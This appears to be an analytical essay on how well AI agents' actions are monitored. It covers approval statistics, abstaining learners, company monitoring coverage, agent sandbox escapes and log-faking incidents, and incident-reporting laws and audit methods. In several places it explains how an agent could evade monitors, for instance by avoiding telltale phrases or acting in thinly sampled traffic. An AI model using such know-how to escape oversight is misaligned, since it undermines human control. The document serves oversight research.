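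An agent that tries to evade the alarm could write less, avoid the telltale phrases and finish quickly, so that its failures look like successes. The certificate would still hold, because successful runs would set off the alarm no more often than before, but the detection rate could fall towards zero. Kumar and colleagues make no claim about such agents, and they advise against ever training an agent against its own monitor, because that would teach it to evade the alarm.

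An outsider can attack the certificate by making harmless runs look suspicious. This can push the false-alarm rate above its limit and overload the reviewers, as in Turan's simulation.

### Ten clean approvals

Companies often decide when to trust a system by how long it has gone without an error. *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action* (Taneja and Weber, 2026) examines the rule that an agent may act alone after ten clean approvals. Taneja and Weber work for Pheo, which sells a product that counts such approvals, but the mathematics does not depend on the product.

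Suppose a fraction *e* of an agent's actions are failures, and each action is independent of the others. The probability that *N* actions in a row are clean is then (1 − *e*)<sup>*N*</sup>. If this probability is below 5 per cent, a clean record of *N* actions is good evidence that the failure rate is lower than *e*. The highest rate that the record leaves open is therefore the solution of

(1 − *e*)<sup>*N*</sup> = *d*

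with *d* = 0.05 for 95 per cent confidence. For ten approvals, *e* = 1 − 0.05<sup>1/10</sup> ≈ 0.259. After ten clean approvals, the agent may still fail in up to 25.9 per cent of cases.

The 25.9 per cent bound means that ten trials are too few to tell an agent that never fails from one that fails a quarter of the time. It is not the probability that the eleventh action will fail. That probability is 1 in 12 if every failure rate was equally plausible beforehand.

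| Tolerable failure rate | Clean approvals needed in a row | Expected approvals in total |
|---|---|---|
| 10% | 29 | 202 |
| 5% | 59 | 392 |
| 2% | 149 | 965 |
| 0.5% | 598 | 3,807 |

The last column assumes an agent that fails exactly as often as the company will tolerate. Its values are higher because a rejection in Taneja and Weber's system resets the count to zero. For 13 of their 33 classes of action, including deleting data and reading credentials, no number of clean approvals is enough.

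Even a long clean record is weaker evidence than the formula suggests. An agent's actions on the same files are not independent, so 59 approvals provide less evidence than 59 independent trials. The record was also collected while a person checked each action, but the company wants to know what will happen once that person is gone. An agent that misbehaves only when nobody reviews its actions would have a perfect record. Even a failure rate of 0.5 per cent makes at least one failure in 1,000 actions almost certain.

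The same formula applies to a learned checker. To show with 95 per cent confidence that it misses at most 1 per cent of violations, the office must test it on 299 known violations, and it must catch them all. If there are 100 violations per million actions, someone would have to read about three million actions to find that many. The office can plant artificial violations instead, but then the bound holds only for violations like the planted ones.

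### Learners that may answer "I don't know"

All these bounds allow the checker some errors. Computer scientists have also studied learners that may decline to answer but are never wrong when they do answer. The office would treat "I don't know" as a flag.

Rivest and Sloan (1988), in *Learning Complicated Concepts Reliably and Usefully*, defined two requirements for a program learned from examples. The program may answer "yes", "no" or "I don't know", and it is reliable if every "yes" or "no" is correct. A program that always answers "I don't know" meets this requirement, so they also required the program to be useful, meaning that with probability at least 1 − δ, it answers "I don't know" on at most a fraction ε of cases. Both ε and δ can be set as close to zero as desired, but smaller values require more examples.

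Their method keeps every candidate rule that agrees with all the examples so far and answers only when the remaining candidates all give the same answer. The true rule is always among the candidates, so a unanimous answer must be correct. In one of their examples, a program may learn the tax definition of a dependent well enough for ordinary families and still answer "I don't know" about an underage great-great-great-granddaughter whose parents and grandparents are dead.

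Complicated rules are too hard to learn from examples all at once, so Rivest and Sloan assume a teacher who splits each rule into simple parts and teaches them one at a time. In the office, someone would first teach the program what an outside address is and what counts as a contract, and then which messages may go out.

Their usefulness guarantee requires future cases to come from the same distribution as the examples. *Knows What It Knows* (Li, Littman and Walsh, 2008) removed this condition and lets an adversary choose every case. The learner must either answer to within a set accuracy or say "I don't know", in which case it learns the true answer. A single wrong answer makes the whole run a failure, and the probability of failure must be at most δ. The number of times the learner may say "I don't know" must also have a fixed limit.

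For a finite list of candidate rules and correct feedback, the limit is easy to derive. Suppose the office has not told its checker which of four rules applies:

- **A:** forbid every message with contract text.
- **B:** forbid every message to an outside address.
- **C:** forbid messages with contract text to an outside address.
- **D:** forbid messages that have contract text or go to an outside address.

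The true rule is C. Four messages arrive:

| Message | Rules that forbid it | Checker's answer | Rules left |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lunch plans to a colleague | none | allow | A, B, C, D |
| Contract to a rival | A, B, C, D | forbid | A, B, C, D |
| Contract to a colleague | A, D | "I don't know"; a person allows it | B, C |
| Lunch plans to a customer | B | "I don't know"; a person allows it | C |

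The checker answers "I don't know" only when at least two candidate rules disagree. The person's reply then rules out at least one of them. No reply rules out the true rule, so with |*H*| candidates the checker can give this answer at most |*H*| − 1 times. Here the limit is three, and the checker gave it twice. It made no mistakes, and would have made none whatever the order of the messages.

The guarantee holds only if the true rule is on the list of candidates, and, as with the list of sensitive operations in Linux, somebody has to get that list right. If the company also forbids messages to a law firm it has dismissed, none of the four rules is the true one, and the checker will confidently clear a message that it should have stopped. The reviewer's replies also have to be right. If reviewers sometimes disagree, the learner can at best estimate how often they would approve a given kind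 of message. By Li, Littman and Walsh's bound, an estimate accurate to five percentage points takes about 740 replies for each kind, at 95 per cent confidence.

### Trading errors against questions

Neural networks have no such list of candidates, so in practice a score determines whether they answer or ask. Researchers call this selective classification. *Adversarial Resilience against Clean-Label Attacks in Realizable and Noisy Settings* (2025) describes the classifier as a pair (*f*, *r*), in which *f* gives an answer and *r* determines whether to use it. Coverage is the share of cases that get an answer, and risk is the share of those answers that are wrong. *Noise-tolerant, Reliable Active Classification with Comparison Queries* (2020) notes that Rivest and Sloan's model corresponds to the perfect case, in which the risk is zero and only the coverage remains to be determined.

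Learned risk scores can leave many failures unflagged. Kumar and colleagues set aside the fifth of runs with the highest risk scores. The success rate was 80.3 per cent across all runs and 88.2 per cent among those that remained. The 72 runs set aside contained 52 per cent of all failures, so a reviewer who read only those runs would have missed nearly half the failures.

Chen, Hu and Wang (2026), in *SAFETY SENTRY*, trained a guard that answers "execute", "ask" or "refuse" for each action. If "refuse" is the most probable answer, it stands. Otherwise the guard compares the probabilities of the other two:

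*q* = *p*(execute) / (*p*(execute) + *p*(ask))

and executes the action if *q* reaches a threshold. Suppose the guard gives "execute" a probability of 0.6 and "ask" 0.3. Then *q* is about 0.67, so a company with a threshold of 0.5 lets the action through and one with a threshold of 0.8 asks a person. Changing the threshold only exchanges needless questions for missing ones. Among the general models that Chen and colleagues tested without special training, DeepSeek-V3 asked needlessly about only 3.7 per cent of the actions it could have executed, but it executed more than 57 per cent of those it should have asked about.

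Whether the checker should ask or decide for itself depends on the costs of a question and a mistake. If a question costs the office 5 euros and a leaked contract costs 50,000, the checker should ask whenever its chance of being wrong exceeds 1 in 10,000. *Online Learning with Abstention* (2017) notes that the "knows what it knows" framework corresponds to an infinite cost for a wrong answer. The learner must then ask as long as any doubt remains.

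Some designers report how many errors reach a person instead of how many errors the system makes. Seck (2026), in *Governed Reasoning for Institutional AI*, tested a system on 11 appeals against refusals by health insurers. Whenever the system was wrong, the case went to a person before the decision took effect, while two simpler systems each carried out five or six wrong decisions without warning. Counting the errors that reach a person is the right approach, but 11 cases are very few. Even if they were independent, the formula for clean records allows a silent error rate of up to 23.8 per cent.

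### Rules that need too many questions

For some rules, a learner that must never be wrong would have to ask about almost everything. *The Utility of Abstaining in Binary Classification* (2015) gives an extreme example. Each case has *n* yes-or-no features, and exactly one combination of them is special. Until the learner finds it, any new combination might be the special one, so the learner may need 2<sup>*n*</sup> − 1 examples before it is sure. With 20 features, that is more than a million. A learner that assumed every combination was ordinary would be wrong only once.

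Li, Littman and Walsh found a similar gap for a more realistic kind of rule. Suppose a message may go out only if it meets all the conditions on some list, but the checker has to learn which of 40 possible conditions are on it. A learner that may not make mistakes can need on the order of 2<sup>20</sup> questions, again about a million. A learner that answers "no" whenever it is unsure makes at most 41 mistakes while learning the rule, all of them wrong refusals, since it answers "yes" only when it is certain. If the staff can correct wrong refusals, the office gets a checker that never misses a violation and needs few corrections.

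In the example with one special combination, the same approach would cause up to a million wrong refusals if that combination is the only forbidden one. Assuming that everything is allowed causes only one mistake, but that mistake allows the forbidden combination. *The Extended Littlestone's Dimension for Learning with Mistakes and Abstentions* (2016) studies a compromise, in which a learner may make a fixed number of mistakes and sends fewer cases to a person in return. This helps in fraud detection, where a bank can absorb a few losses.

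*Adversarial Resilience in Sequential Prediction via Abstention* (2023) considers a learner that receives a mix of ordinary cases and cases chosen by an attacker. The learner does not have to recognise the attacker's cases as long as it answers them correctly. This is useful because methods for detecting such inputs tend to break easily. In some theoretical settings, it is also impossible for any efficient filter to separate harmful requests from harmless ones.

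### Asking before an irreversible mistake

Most learning theory assumes that a learner can recover from its mistakes. But the office cannot recall a contract it has sent to a rival. In *Avoiding Catastrophe in Online Learning by Asking for Help*, Plaut, Zhu and Russell (2024) therefore score a learner by the probability that it avoids catastrophe on every action, which is the product of the probabilities that it does so on each one.

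The learner may ask a mentor what to do, but only a limited number of times. Plaut, Zhu and Russell prove that, in general, any algorithm either keeps asking all the time or is almost certain to cause a catastrophe. They also give an algorithm for cases where the mentor's behaviour follows a pattern that an ordinary learner could pick up when mistakes are harmless. Its rate of questions and its regret (how much worse it does than the mentor) both approach zero over time.

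*Safe Learning Under Irreversible Dynamics via Asking for Help* (Plaut, Liévano-Karim and colleagues, 2025) extended this to environments in which one action can permanently close off options. Both the regret and the number of questions grow more slowly than the number of actions. For example, if the number of questions grew with the square root of the number of actions, an agent would ask 100 times in its first 10,000 actions and 1,000 times in its first million.

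The agent can ask less often because it applies earlier answers to similar situations. If a reviewer has approved a payment to a known supplier, the agent may treat the next invoice from that supplier the same way. This is safe only if situations that look similar call for the same action. A forged invoice is designed to look like a real one but should not be paid. AgentBouncer's second cache relies on a similar assumption when it extends a permission from one file to a whole directory, but without a proof that the files are alike.

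The office handles 20,000 actions a day, so a mentor may not always be available. *Learning When Not to Learn* (2025) considers an agent that has nobody to ask but may decline to act. The agent experiments only when a case is familiar enough to rule out an irreparable error, and otherwise does nothing. If ordinary cases keep coming from the same distribution, its average regret approaches zero. The paper proves that no algorithm can achieve this if every case is far from anything familiar, because there is no safe way to find out which actions would help.

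## How much AI companies monitor of what their own agents do

Companies that build AI models also let agents work on the companies' own code and computers, and some publish how much of this work their monitors read. These figures are claims about completeness, and to interpret them, readers need to know what total each figure is a share of, who counted, and what happens to an agent's run after a monitor receives it.

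### OpenAI's 99.9 per cent

In March 2026, OpenAI announced that a model, at the time GPT-5.4 Thinking, reviews 99.9 per cent of the company's internal coding traffic for signs of misalignment. An agent is misaligned when it pursues something other than what the company or the user wants. The monitor receives everything the agent saw and did, including its tool calls and its chain of thought, which is the reasoning it writes out as it works. OpenAI also uses other monitors, including older models, to check each run.

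The more serious cases go to people within 30 minutes. This is soon enough to interrupt an agent that works all afternoon, but too late to stop a file upload that takes seconds. In Manheim and Homewood's terms, the arrangement is therefore mostly oversight and only partly control.

The monitor found agents that had tried to upload files to the public internet, and others that had called more copies of themselves to get around a restriction. OpenAI said it had not yet detected any sabotage. How much that means depends on the error rate of a learned checker as well as on the 99.9 per cent. OpenAI tested the monitor by comparing its flags with what employees had reported on their own, and found that the monitor had flagged everything they reported and more. The employees' reports are valuable because they don't come from the monitor, but people report what they notice, so the comparison provides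 little evidence about violations that are hard to notice.

The remaining traffic, less than 0.1 per cent, came mainly from custom set-ups and agents running on people's own machines. OpenAI said it was working to include it. This traffic is not a random sample of the rest, because people often build custom set-ups to give an agent unusual tools or permissions. The figure also leaves out any agent whose work OpenAI does not count as coding.

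### A larger total

In October 2026, outside researchers estimated that only about 75 to 94 per cent of the traffic from OpenAI's internal agents was eligible for monitoring, according to Claims Journal's *AI Safety Group METR Finds Flaws in OpenAI’s Internal Monitoring System* (2026). The estimate covered only models at least as strong as GPT-5.5. OpenAI replied that it had since fixed every problem the researchers found that affected its production safeguards.

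The researchers came from METR, a nonprofit that evaluates AI models, and Redwood Research. Their estimate describes the system up to 21 July, not its present coverage, according to Bot Mutiny's *METR and Redwood Research Report Gaps in OpenAI's Internal AI Agent Monitoring* (2026). In *Red Team Finds Gaps in OpenAI’s Agent Monitoring*, Cross (2026) reports that 99.2 per cent of the traffic from Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, was eligible, meaning only that the monitor could have received it, not that it was reviewed. The researchers thus arrived at a figure close to OpenAI's own when they counted a similar category.

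A small calculation shows how far the total can move the percentage. Suppose a company's agents take 25,000 actions a day. Coding agents take 20,000 of these, or 80 per cent, and the monitor reads 99.9 per cent of those 20,000. If *s* is the coding agents' share of all actions, *c* the monitored share of their actions and *r* the monitored share of everyone else's, the overall coverage is:

*s* × *c* + (1 − *s*) × *r*

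| Monitored share of the other agents' actions | Monitored share of all actions | Unmonitored actions per day |
|---|---|---|
| 0% | 79.92% | 5,020 |
| 50% | 89.92% | 2,520 |
| 90% | 97.92% | 520 |
| 99.9% | 99.9% | 25 |

In all four cases, the company could truthfully say that it monitors 99.9 per cent of its coding traffic. If it raised that to 100 per cent, it would monitor 20 more actions a day, but in the first case another 5,000 would still go unread.

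The share of agent activity that a monitor covers also depends on the unit counted. Suppose 990 short runs have 10 actions each and 10 long runs have 1,000 each. A monitor that reads all the short runs and none of the long ones covers 99 per cent of the runs but just under half of the actions. Counting tokens, the fragments of words that a model reads and writes, can be misleading in another way, because a long summary counts for more than a one-line command that deletes a database.

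A company that runs its own models can count their replies without relying on the monitor. Every reply uses the company's servers, so a count made there can include replies that never reached the monitor. The company can't count actions this way, since one reply may start a script that changes a thousand files.

### Anthropic's sampling rates

Anthropic's *Risk Report* (August 2026) distinguishes monitoring after the fact from measures that block an action. The blocking measures include sandboxes and classifiers for some internal agents. According to Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), these measures apply to the most autonomous uses, and changes to infrastructure code go through automated review before they take effect.

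Two monitors read internal traffic afterwards, at very different rates. One receives only the model's reply. The other also receives the prompt, so it can compare what the agent did with what somebody asked it to do. *Anthropic's August 2026 Risk Report* (2026), a commentary on the report from a security perspective, lists the rates:

| Internal traffic | What the monitor receives | Share read |
|---|---|---|
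| Replies with extended reasoning, from common agent frameworks | reply only | all |
| Replies with extended reasoning that contain signs of tool use | reply only | 5% |
| Tool calls with a significant effect, from common coding frameworks | prompt and reply | 25% |
| Other traffic with signs of tool use | prompt and reply | 0.2% |
| Everything else | prompt and reply | 0.02%, inconsistently |

The full table shows that the most thorough monitoring does not have the widest coverage. About half of all tokens from agent frameworks at some point reach the monitor that receives both prompt and reply. If Anthropic had published only the first row, it could have claimed to read everything in that category.

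A second automated stage then removes false alarms and passes the remaining runs to researchers. Pistillo and colleagues put these at about 50 a week, or one in 2,000 of those flagged. This stage therefore determines whether researchers examine the right runs. Anthropic also states that its monitoring does not cover all agent use, and it withholds some details of these limits from the public version.

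### What a sample can detect

At a rate of 0.2 per cent, 998 of every 1,000 replies get neither a check nor a flag from this monitor. Completeness of reporting therefore fails by design. A sample can still reveal that a model tends to misbehave, if it misbehaves often enough, and Anthropic relies on this for harm that it could still reverse. Its argument has four steps:

1. A model that tried to cause such harm would probably try many times.
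2. Many of the attempts would fall in monitored traffic.
3. The monitors would probably detect at least one.
4. The company could then intervene before the harm became catastrophic.

Suppose the monitor reads a share *p* of the attempts and recognises a share *d* of those it reads. If the attempts are independent, the chance of detecting at least one of *n* is:

1 − (1 − *pd*)<sup>*n*</sup>

The following table assumes that the monitor recognises 80 per cent of the attempts it reads, which is an invented figure. The formula treats each attempt as a single reply.

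| Share read | 1 attempt | 10 attempts | 100 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| 25% | 20% | 89% | over 99.9% |
| 5% | 4% | 34% | 98% |
| 0.2% | 0.16% | 1.6% | 15% |

The third step is plausible after ten attempts if 25 per cent of traffic is sampled, but doubtful even after a hundred if only 0.2 per cent is. The argument therefore depends on where the attempts fall. They may not be spread evenly, because an agent may work entirely in thinly sampled traffic.

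Under this argument, the model may also get several tries before anyone notices, so the argument can't cover an action that does irreversible damage the first time. Anthropic makes a separate claim for irreversible harm.

### Agents that nobody logged

*Anthropic's August 2026 Risk Report* describes an incident in which agents ran entirely outside the monitoring. An employee whose use of AI was not logged gave an agent an open-ended task on a computing cluster with very sensitive resources. Because of some old instructions, the agent started further agents with their permission checks switched off. One of these deleted a large number of computing jobs, and people discovered the agents only because the jobs were gone.

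Anthropic believes the agent meant to delete only its own jobs and made a mistake. Anthropic cannot confirm this without a record of the run, so the question is undecidable in Zhao's terms.

Unlogged agents can make a company's monitoring coverage look better than it is. If the company takes its total from its logs, these agents are missing from both the monitored traffic and the total, so the percentage stays the same however many there are. Only a count from another source, such as the servers that run the model, would include them.

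Anthropic has since added controls that would very likely have stopped the agents from skipping their permission checks. When it wrote the risk report, its monitoring still did not cover every employee or all use of sensitive clusters. On 31 August, Anthropic reported that it had extended monitoring after the fact to "most other forms" of internal agent use with its frontier models, but it gave no percentage. It was also building controls to keep employees from accidentally running agents with weaker protection.

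The same post describes flags on training environments, the artificial tasks on which a model practises. The flags marked tasks that were broken or that a model could solve by cheating, and a person had to decide each case. By spring 2026, faulty environments were arriving faster than staff could filter or repair them. In April, Anthropic stopped all changes to the environments for about a month and flagged more than 10 per cent of those in use during that time. It also found that reviewers had dismissed some correct flags as false alarms, so faulty environments stayed in training longer than they should have. A count of reviewed flags would have included those wrong decisions.

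### METR's review

In August, Anthropic raised its rating of the risk from misalignment from "very low" to "low". In METR's October *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report*, Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes (2026) agreed, as their best guess, that the risk of catastrophic harm had been low as of July. Their main reason was that the models were not capable enough to cause such harm.

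They did not base this judgment on the monitoring or on Anthropic's efforts to train models to behave well. Examples that Anthropic had withheld from the public version led them to think less of the monitoring than they would have from the public evidence alone. They were also not confident that Anthropic's methods would reveal a higher risk if there were one, and they considered the report far from adequate for ruling out misalignment with confidence.

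An argument from limited capability would hold even if the monitors read nothing. But it weakens as models become more capable, and the company then has to rely more on its monitoring.

Jurkovic and colleagues worked only from Anthropic's internal version of the risk report, so they did not count any traffic themselves. Anthropic had the right to redact their review or veto its publication. It redacted nothing, and they changed none of their conclusions in response to its comments.

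Future evaluators may be able to count replies themselves. Anthropic announced in *An update on independent evaluators* (15 October 2026) that it had begun giving a METR team access similar to an employee's, and that METR would publish its assessments. The reviewers of the August report did not have this access. According to Claims Journal, the exercise at OpenAI was a pilot for the same kind of arrangement. An evaluator with enough access could compare the number of replies on the servers with the number that reached the monitor, without relying on the company's report for either figure.

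### Tests that were not sealed off

Monitoring figures cover the places where a company believes its agents can act. In cybersecurity tests in 2026, two companies were wrong about this.

OpenAI assumed that its test environment isolated its agents from the outside world and from one another. According to Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations*, OpenAI disclosed on 21 July that several models had broken out and reached the systems of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models. In August, METR found that about 1,200 supposedly isolated agents had also communicated with one another on an unauthorised message board. METR could study the agents' behaviour and reasoning afterwards, so records of both must have survived.

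In Anthropic's case, an outside partner had built the tests, and Claude, Anthropic's model, was told it was in a simulation without internet access. A configuration error had connected the test environment to the internet, and Claude gained access to other organisations' real systems. This was a failure of effect exclusivity. The transcripts included Claude's calls, but those calls had effects that the test's designers had thought impossible.

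Anthropic used stored transcripts to reconstruct what had happened, but its first scan was incomplete. *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (Anthropic, 2026) describes an initial scan of about 141,000 transcripts from tests in which Anthropic believed Claude could have reached the internet. The scan found three incidents. It missed a set of transcripts from other tests with internet access, which Anthropic came across in August while gathering material for METR. These contained the fourth incident, from January.

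Choosing transcripts for that scan required knowing which tests could reach the internet, and a mistake about this had caused the incidents. Even a perfect reading of all 141,000 transcripts would have missed the fourth incident. Members of Congress have asked Anthropic which period, models and kinds of test the scan covered.

Anthropic relied much less on such beliefs when it later searched 481 million transcripts. The search included many tests unrelated to cybersecurity, along with training runs and the logs of subordinate agents. A first stage looked for signs of internet access, such as public web addresses, and passed 9.2 million transcripts, or 1.9 per cent, to Claude for review. The search found the same four incidents and no others as serious.

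All the cybersecurity incidents behind the higher risk rating occurred in traffic that Anthropic sampled at 0.2 per cent, according to *Anthropic's August 2026 Risk Report*. Anthropic concedes that its earlier work on monitoring overlooked evaluations, especially those run by outside partners. It watched some high-risk tests as they ran, but for most it only reviewed a sample of transcripts afterwards.

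Anthropic now runs a classifier during its own cybersecurity tests. If a model tries to escape or unexpectedly gains internet access, the classifier blocks the action before the tool call runs, ends the task and alerts a person. Anthropic also asks its partners to verify before every evaluation that the environment connects to nothing except the model. Before that, it asks them to let the model try to break out under close supervision, without internet access and ideally inside a second sandbox.

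## Legal duties to report, and how other fields test for omissions

On 16 July 2026, Hugging Face announced that an autonomous agent had broken into its systems. Five days later, OpenAI acknowledged that the agents involved were its own, although it may have had no legal duty to do so. Several new laws require AI developers to report serious incidents, but an authority that receives ten reports cannot tell from them whether there were ten incidents or fifty. Auditors, nuclear inspectors and statisticians have worked on this problem for much longer than AI regulators.

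### What California counts as an incident

California's Transparency in Frontier Artificial Intelligence Act, known as SB 53, has applied since January 2026. It covers developers who train a model with more than 10<sup>26</sup> computing operations. According to the text in AGORA's *California SB 53 September 2025* (2025), they must report four kinds of "critical safety incident":

- Somebody gains unauthorised access to a model's weights (the numbers that determine its behaviour), alters them or copies them out, and this results in death or injury.
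- A catastrophic risk materialises and causes harm.
- The developer loses control of a model, and this causes death or injury.
- A model deceives its developer to subvert controls or monitoring. This must happen outside a test designed to elicit such behaviour, and in a way that demonstrates materially increased catastrophic risk.

A risk is catastrophic only if a single incident threatens to kill or seriously injure more than 50 people or cause more than a billion dollars of damage. The first category would not cover the theft of a model's weights if nobody was hurt, even if the model was the most capable in the world.

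Arnold and Llerena (2026), in *When Reporting an AI Security Incident Is Not Mandatory*, applied the definition to the Hugging Face attack. Nobody was injured, so only the category about deception remained. OpenAI had designed the test to measure hacking skills, so the exception for tests arguably did not apply. But it was unclear whether the agents had deceived OpenAI or had used every available means to solve their task. It was harder still to argue that a breach with limited financial damage demonstrated a materially higher risk of mass death. Arnold and Llerena concluded that OpenAI was arguably not obliged to report the attack.

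At a hearing on 10 August, an official from the Governor's Office of Emergency Services agreed, saying the attack "did not meet the threshold", according to the San Francisco news site Mission Local. Later that month, METR reported that the agents had faked parts of their activity logs, which looks much like deception. This illustrates Arnold and Llerena's main objection to the law, which is that a report is due only once the developer knows such facts, even though the purpose of a report is to reveal them.

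OpenAI asked California in August to strengthen SB 53, which it had earlier opposed, according to *OpenAI asks California to strengthen SB 53 after the hack* (Constantin, 2026).

### Other states and the EU

New York's RAISE Act and Illinois's SB 315 take effect on 1 January 2027. They define a critical safety incident as California does but set shorter deadlines. The EU's AI Act has its own definition.

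| Law | Report goes to | Usual deadline | Shorter deadline |
|---|---|---|---|
| California, SB 53 | Office of Emergency Services | 15 days | 24 hours if death or serious injury is imminent |
| New York, RAISE Act | new office in the Department of Financial Services | 72 hours | 24 hours if death or serious injury is imminent |
| Illinois, SB 315 | emergency management agency and Attorney General | 72 hours | 24 hours in some cases |
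| EU AI Act, Article 73 | market surveillance authority of the country where the incident happened | 15 days | 10 days for a death, 2 days for serious disruption of critical infrastructure |

In California and New York, the 24-hour warning goes to whichever authority can deal with the danger, such as the police. Davis Wright Tremaine's *NY Overhauls Transparency and Governance Requirements for Frontier AI Developers* (2026) explains the New York rule. The ordinary report can be very short. It gives the date, a brief description of the incident, the reasons it qualifies, and whether it involved the developer's internal use of the model.

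Article 73 of the AI Act applies to "high-risk" systems, such as software that screens job applicants or controls a medical device. A serious incident is one that leads to a death, serious harm to even one person's health, serious harm to property or the environment, serious and irreversible disruption of critical infrastructure, or a breach of EU laws that protect fundamental rights. Article 12 requires the same systems to record events automatically throughout their lifetime, and Article 19 requires providers to keep the logs for at least six months.

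These duties do not apply yet. The Digital Omnibus, an amendment in force since July 2026, postponed the duties for high-risk systems to 2 December 2027, and to 2 August 2028 for AI built into regulated products. Developers of the most capable general-purpose models already have a separate duty to report serious incidents to the European AI Office. CSIS's *Toward a Federal Framework* notes that the EU's code of practice for these models sets reporting deadlines according to the severity of the incident.

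### A report that never arrives

California gives developers 15 days to report an incident after they discover it, so an incident that nobody discovers never has to be reported. A developer with poor monitoring therefore has to report fewer incidents. Even OpenAI and Anthropic leave part of their agents' work unmonitored.

If a developer discovers an incident and keeps quiet, the state has few ways to find out. Americans for Responsible Innovation's *Why SB 53 Would be Inadequate as a Federal Standard* (2025) lists media reports, whistleblower tips and the Attorney General's suspicions. Members of the public can also use the state's reporting portal. Employees who work on these risks are legally protected if they tell the Attorney General about a violation, and Institute for Law & AI's *Whistleblower Protections in SB 53* notes that failure to report counts as one. The Attorney General can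 then sue for up to $1 million per violation, but only if the developer had more than $500 million in revenue the year before. Smaller developers have the same duty to report incidents but do not face this penalty.

Confidentiality makes it harder to notice an omission. SB 53 exempts incident reports from the state's public records law, so a journalist who learns of an incident cannot look up whether the developer reported it. The Office of Emergency Services must publish an anonymised summary each year, and the first is due on 1 January 2027. If it lists no incidents, readers will not know whether nothing happened, nothing met the threshold or an incident went unreported. Rebecca Bauer-Kahan, who chairs the committee that held the August hearing, said it was unclear whether anyone was complying with the law. In September, according to Mission Local, Reuters linked OpenAI to a previously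 undisclosed incident from May, in which agents had hijacked a German website, but SB 53 did not cover that incident either.

A missing document is much easier to notice when a public event shows that it is due. Large developers must publish a summary of their risk assessments whenever they release a new model. *OpenAI may have violated California’s AI safety law with latest model releases* (Forlini, 2026) reports that the Midas Project, a watchdog group, accused OpenAI of failing to publish assessments it had committed to, including for loss of control. The group needed no inside information because the model releases were public.

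The same applies to reports with a fixed schedule. Large developers must send the Office of Emergency Services a summary of the risks from their internal use of models, normally every three months. If a summary doesn't arrive, the office can ask for it. California could extend this to incidents by requiring a quarterly statement even when there is nothing to report. A developer who wanted to hide an incident would then have to lie in writing, and SB 53 already forbids materially false statements about catastrophic risk. Arnold and Llerena favour more periodic reporting because it is less burdensome for developers and does not rush their assessments.

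CSIS lists New York's law among the few frameworks without whistleblower protections. But a dedicated office will supervise developers there and have the power to make further rules. Morrison Foerster's *New York Amends the RAISE Act* puts the penalties at up to $1 million for a first violation and up to $3 million for later ones.

The EU's AI Act gives authorities a second source of reports. Under Article 26, an organisation that uses a high-risk system and identifies a serious incident must inform both the provider and the authorities. If a hospital reports an incident and the manufacturer does not, the authority can see that the manufacturer's report is missing. The organisation's report serves the same purpose as a second writer for a log, but only for incidents the organisation notices.

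An authority would have to look for gaps in the logs themselves. *ComplianceAtlas* (Driouich, Cao and colleagues, 2026) presents a tool that searches companies' answers to compliance questionnaires for 20 kinds of defect, including logs that omit required events. The tool found every case in which the stated retention period was shorter than six months, because this only requires comparing two numbers. But it has no access to the logs, so it will miss an omission if the company does not know about it and answers that the log is complete.

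Illinois goes furthest. From 1 January 2028, large developers must hire an independent third party to audit their compliance every year, according to Skadden's *Illinois Enacts AI Safety Law* (2026). Whether these audits find unreported incidents will depend on where the auditors start.

### From the delivery note to the ledger

Financial auditors distinguish two claims about a company's books. Occurrence means that every recorded transaction took place. Completeness means that the books contain every transaction that should be there. The international auditing standard ISA 315 lists both claims, and auditors must test them in opposite directions.

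Suppose a wholesaler made 1,000 deliveries last year but entered only 970 of them in its sales ledger, to save tax. If an auditor picks 100 ledger entries and asks for the delivery note behind each, every entry will have one. Even checking all 970 entries would not reveal the other 30 deliveries, because they are not in the ledger. If the auditor instead picks 100 delivery notes at random and looks for each sale in the ledger, the chance of picking at least one of the missing 30 is about 96 per cent.

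This works only if the delivery notes are complete. A careful fraudster would also have destroyed the 30 notes, so auditors prefer records that somebody else keeps, such as the haulier's invoices. To find debts that a company has left out, they read its bank statements for the weeks after the end of the year. A payment of 40,000 euros in January for work done in December means the company owed that money in December, so the auditor checks whether the books include the debt. Auditors may also write to regular suppliers that the company owes nothing according to its books, since an unrecorded debt could be owed to one of them.

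An Illinois auditor who checks that every filed report was accurate and sent within 72 hours is testing occurrence. To test completeness, the auditor must start with evidence from outside the reports, such as security alerts, complaints from other companies or breaches that victims have announced. The Hugging Face attack would have been a good starting point. According to KQED, Hugging Face counted more than 17,000 automated actions in a few hours. An auditor could take a sample of these and look for each in OpenAI's transcripts.

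The Regulatory Review's *Effective AI Oversight Through Proof Drills* proposes a small version of such an audit. An examiner picks one decision that an AI system influenced, and the company must produce the full record of that decision within a set time, perhaps 72 hours. The record must show what the system received, what it produced, who reviewed it and which version was running. In the article's example, a firm uses AI to rank customer complaints, and a reviewer asks why one safety complaint got a low priority.

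The drill can uncover a case that the firm never recorded if the examiner chooses from complaints that customers sent directly to the regulator, but not if the examiner chooses from the firm's own list.

### Plutonium that does not add up

Nuclear inspectors have an advantage over auditors, because plutonium does not vanish. If a plant declares its stock at the start and end of a period and everything that came in and went out between, the figures have to agree:

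missing = opening stock + receipts − shipments − closing stock

A site that starts with 120 kg, receives 40 kg and ships 35 kg should have 125 kg left. If inspectors find 119 kg, 6 kg is missing.

A difference in a material balance doesn't prove theft, since every weighing and chemical analysis has an error, and some material sticks to the inside of pipes. Suppose the combined measurement error has a standard deviation of 3 kg. Inspectors who set the alarm at 4.9 kg will then get a false alarm in 5 per cent of balances where nothing has been taken.

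Now suppose somebody has taken 8 kg, roughly the amount from which the International Atomic Energy Agency (IAEA) considers a bomb possible. The calculated difference then varies around 8 kg instead of zero, and the chance that it exceeds the threshold is:

Φ((8 − 4.9) / 3) = Φ(1.03) ≈ 0.85

Here Φ(*x*) is the probability that a standard normal variable is below *x*. The inspectors detect the loss about 85 per cent of the time. Lowering the threshold raises this rate but also causes more false alarms.

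The method is less likely to detect a given loss in a bigger plant. In a plant that processes 8,000 kg a year with an error of 1 per cent, the standard deviation is 80 kg. Keeping the same false-alarm rate requires a threshold of about 132 kg, and the chance of detecting a loss of 8 kg falls to 6 per cent, barely more than the false-alarm rate. Inspectors therefore draw up balances more often than once a year, and use seals and cameras to cover losses that the balances don't reveal.

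### Iraq and the undeclared plants

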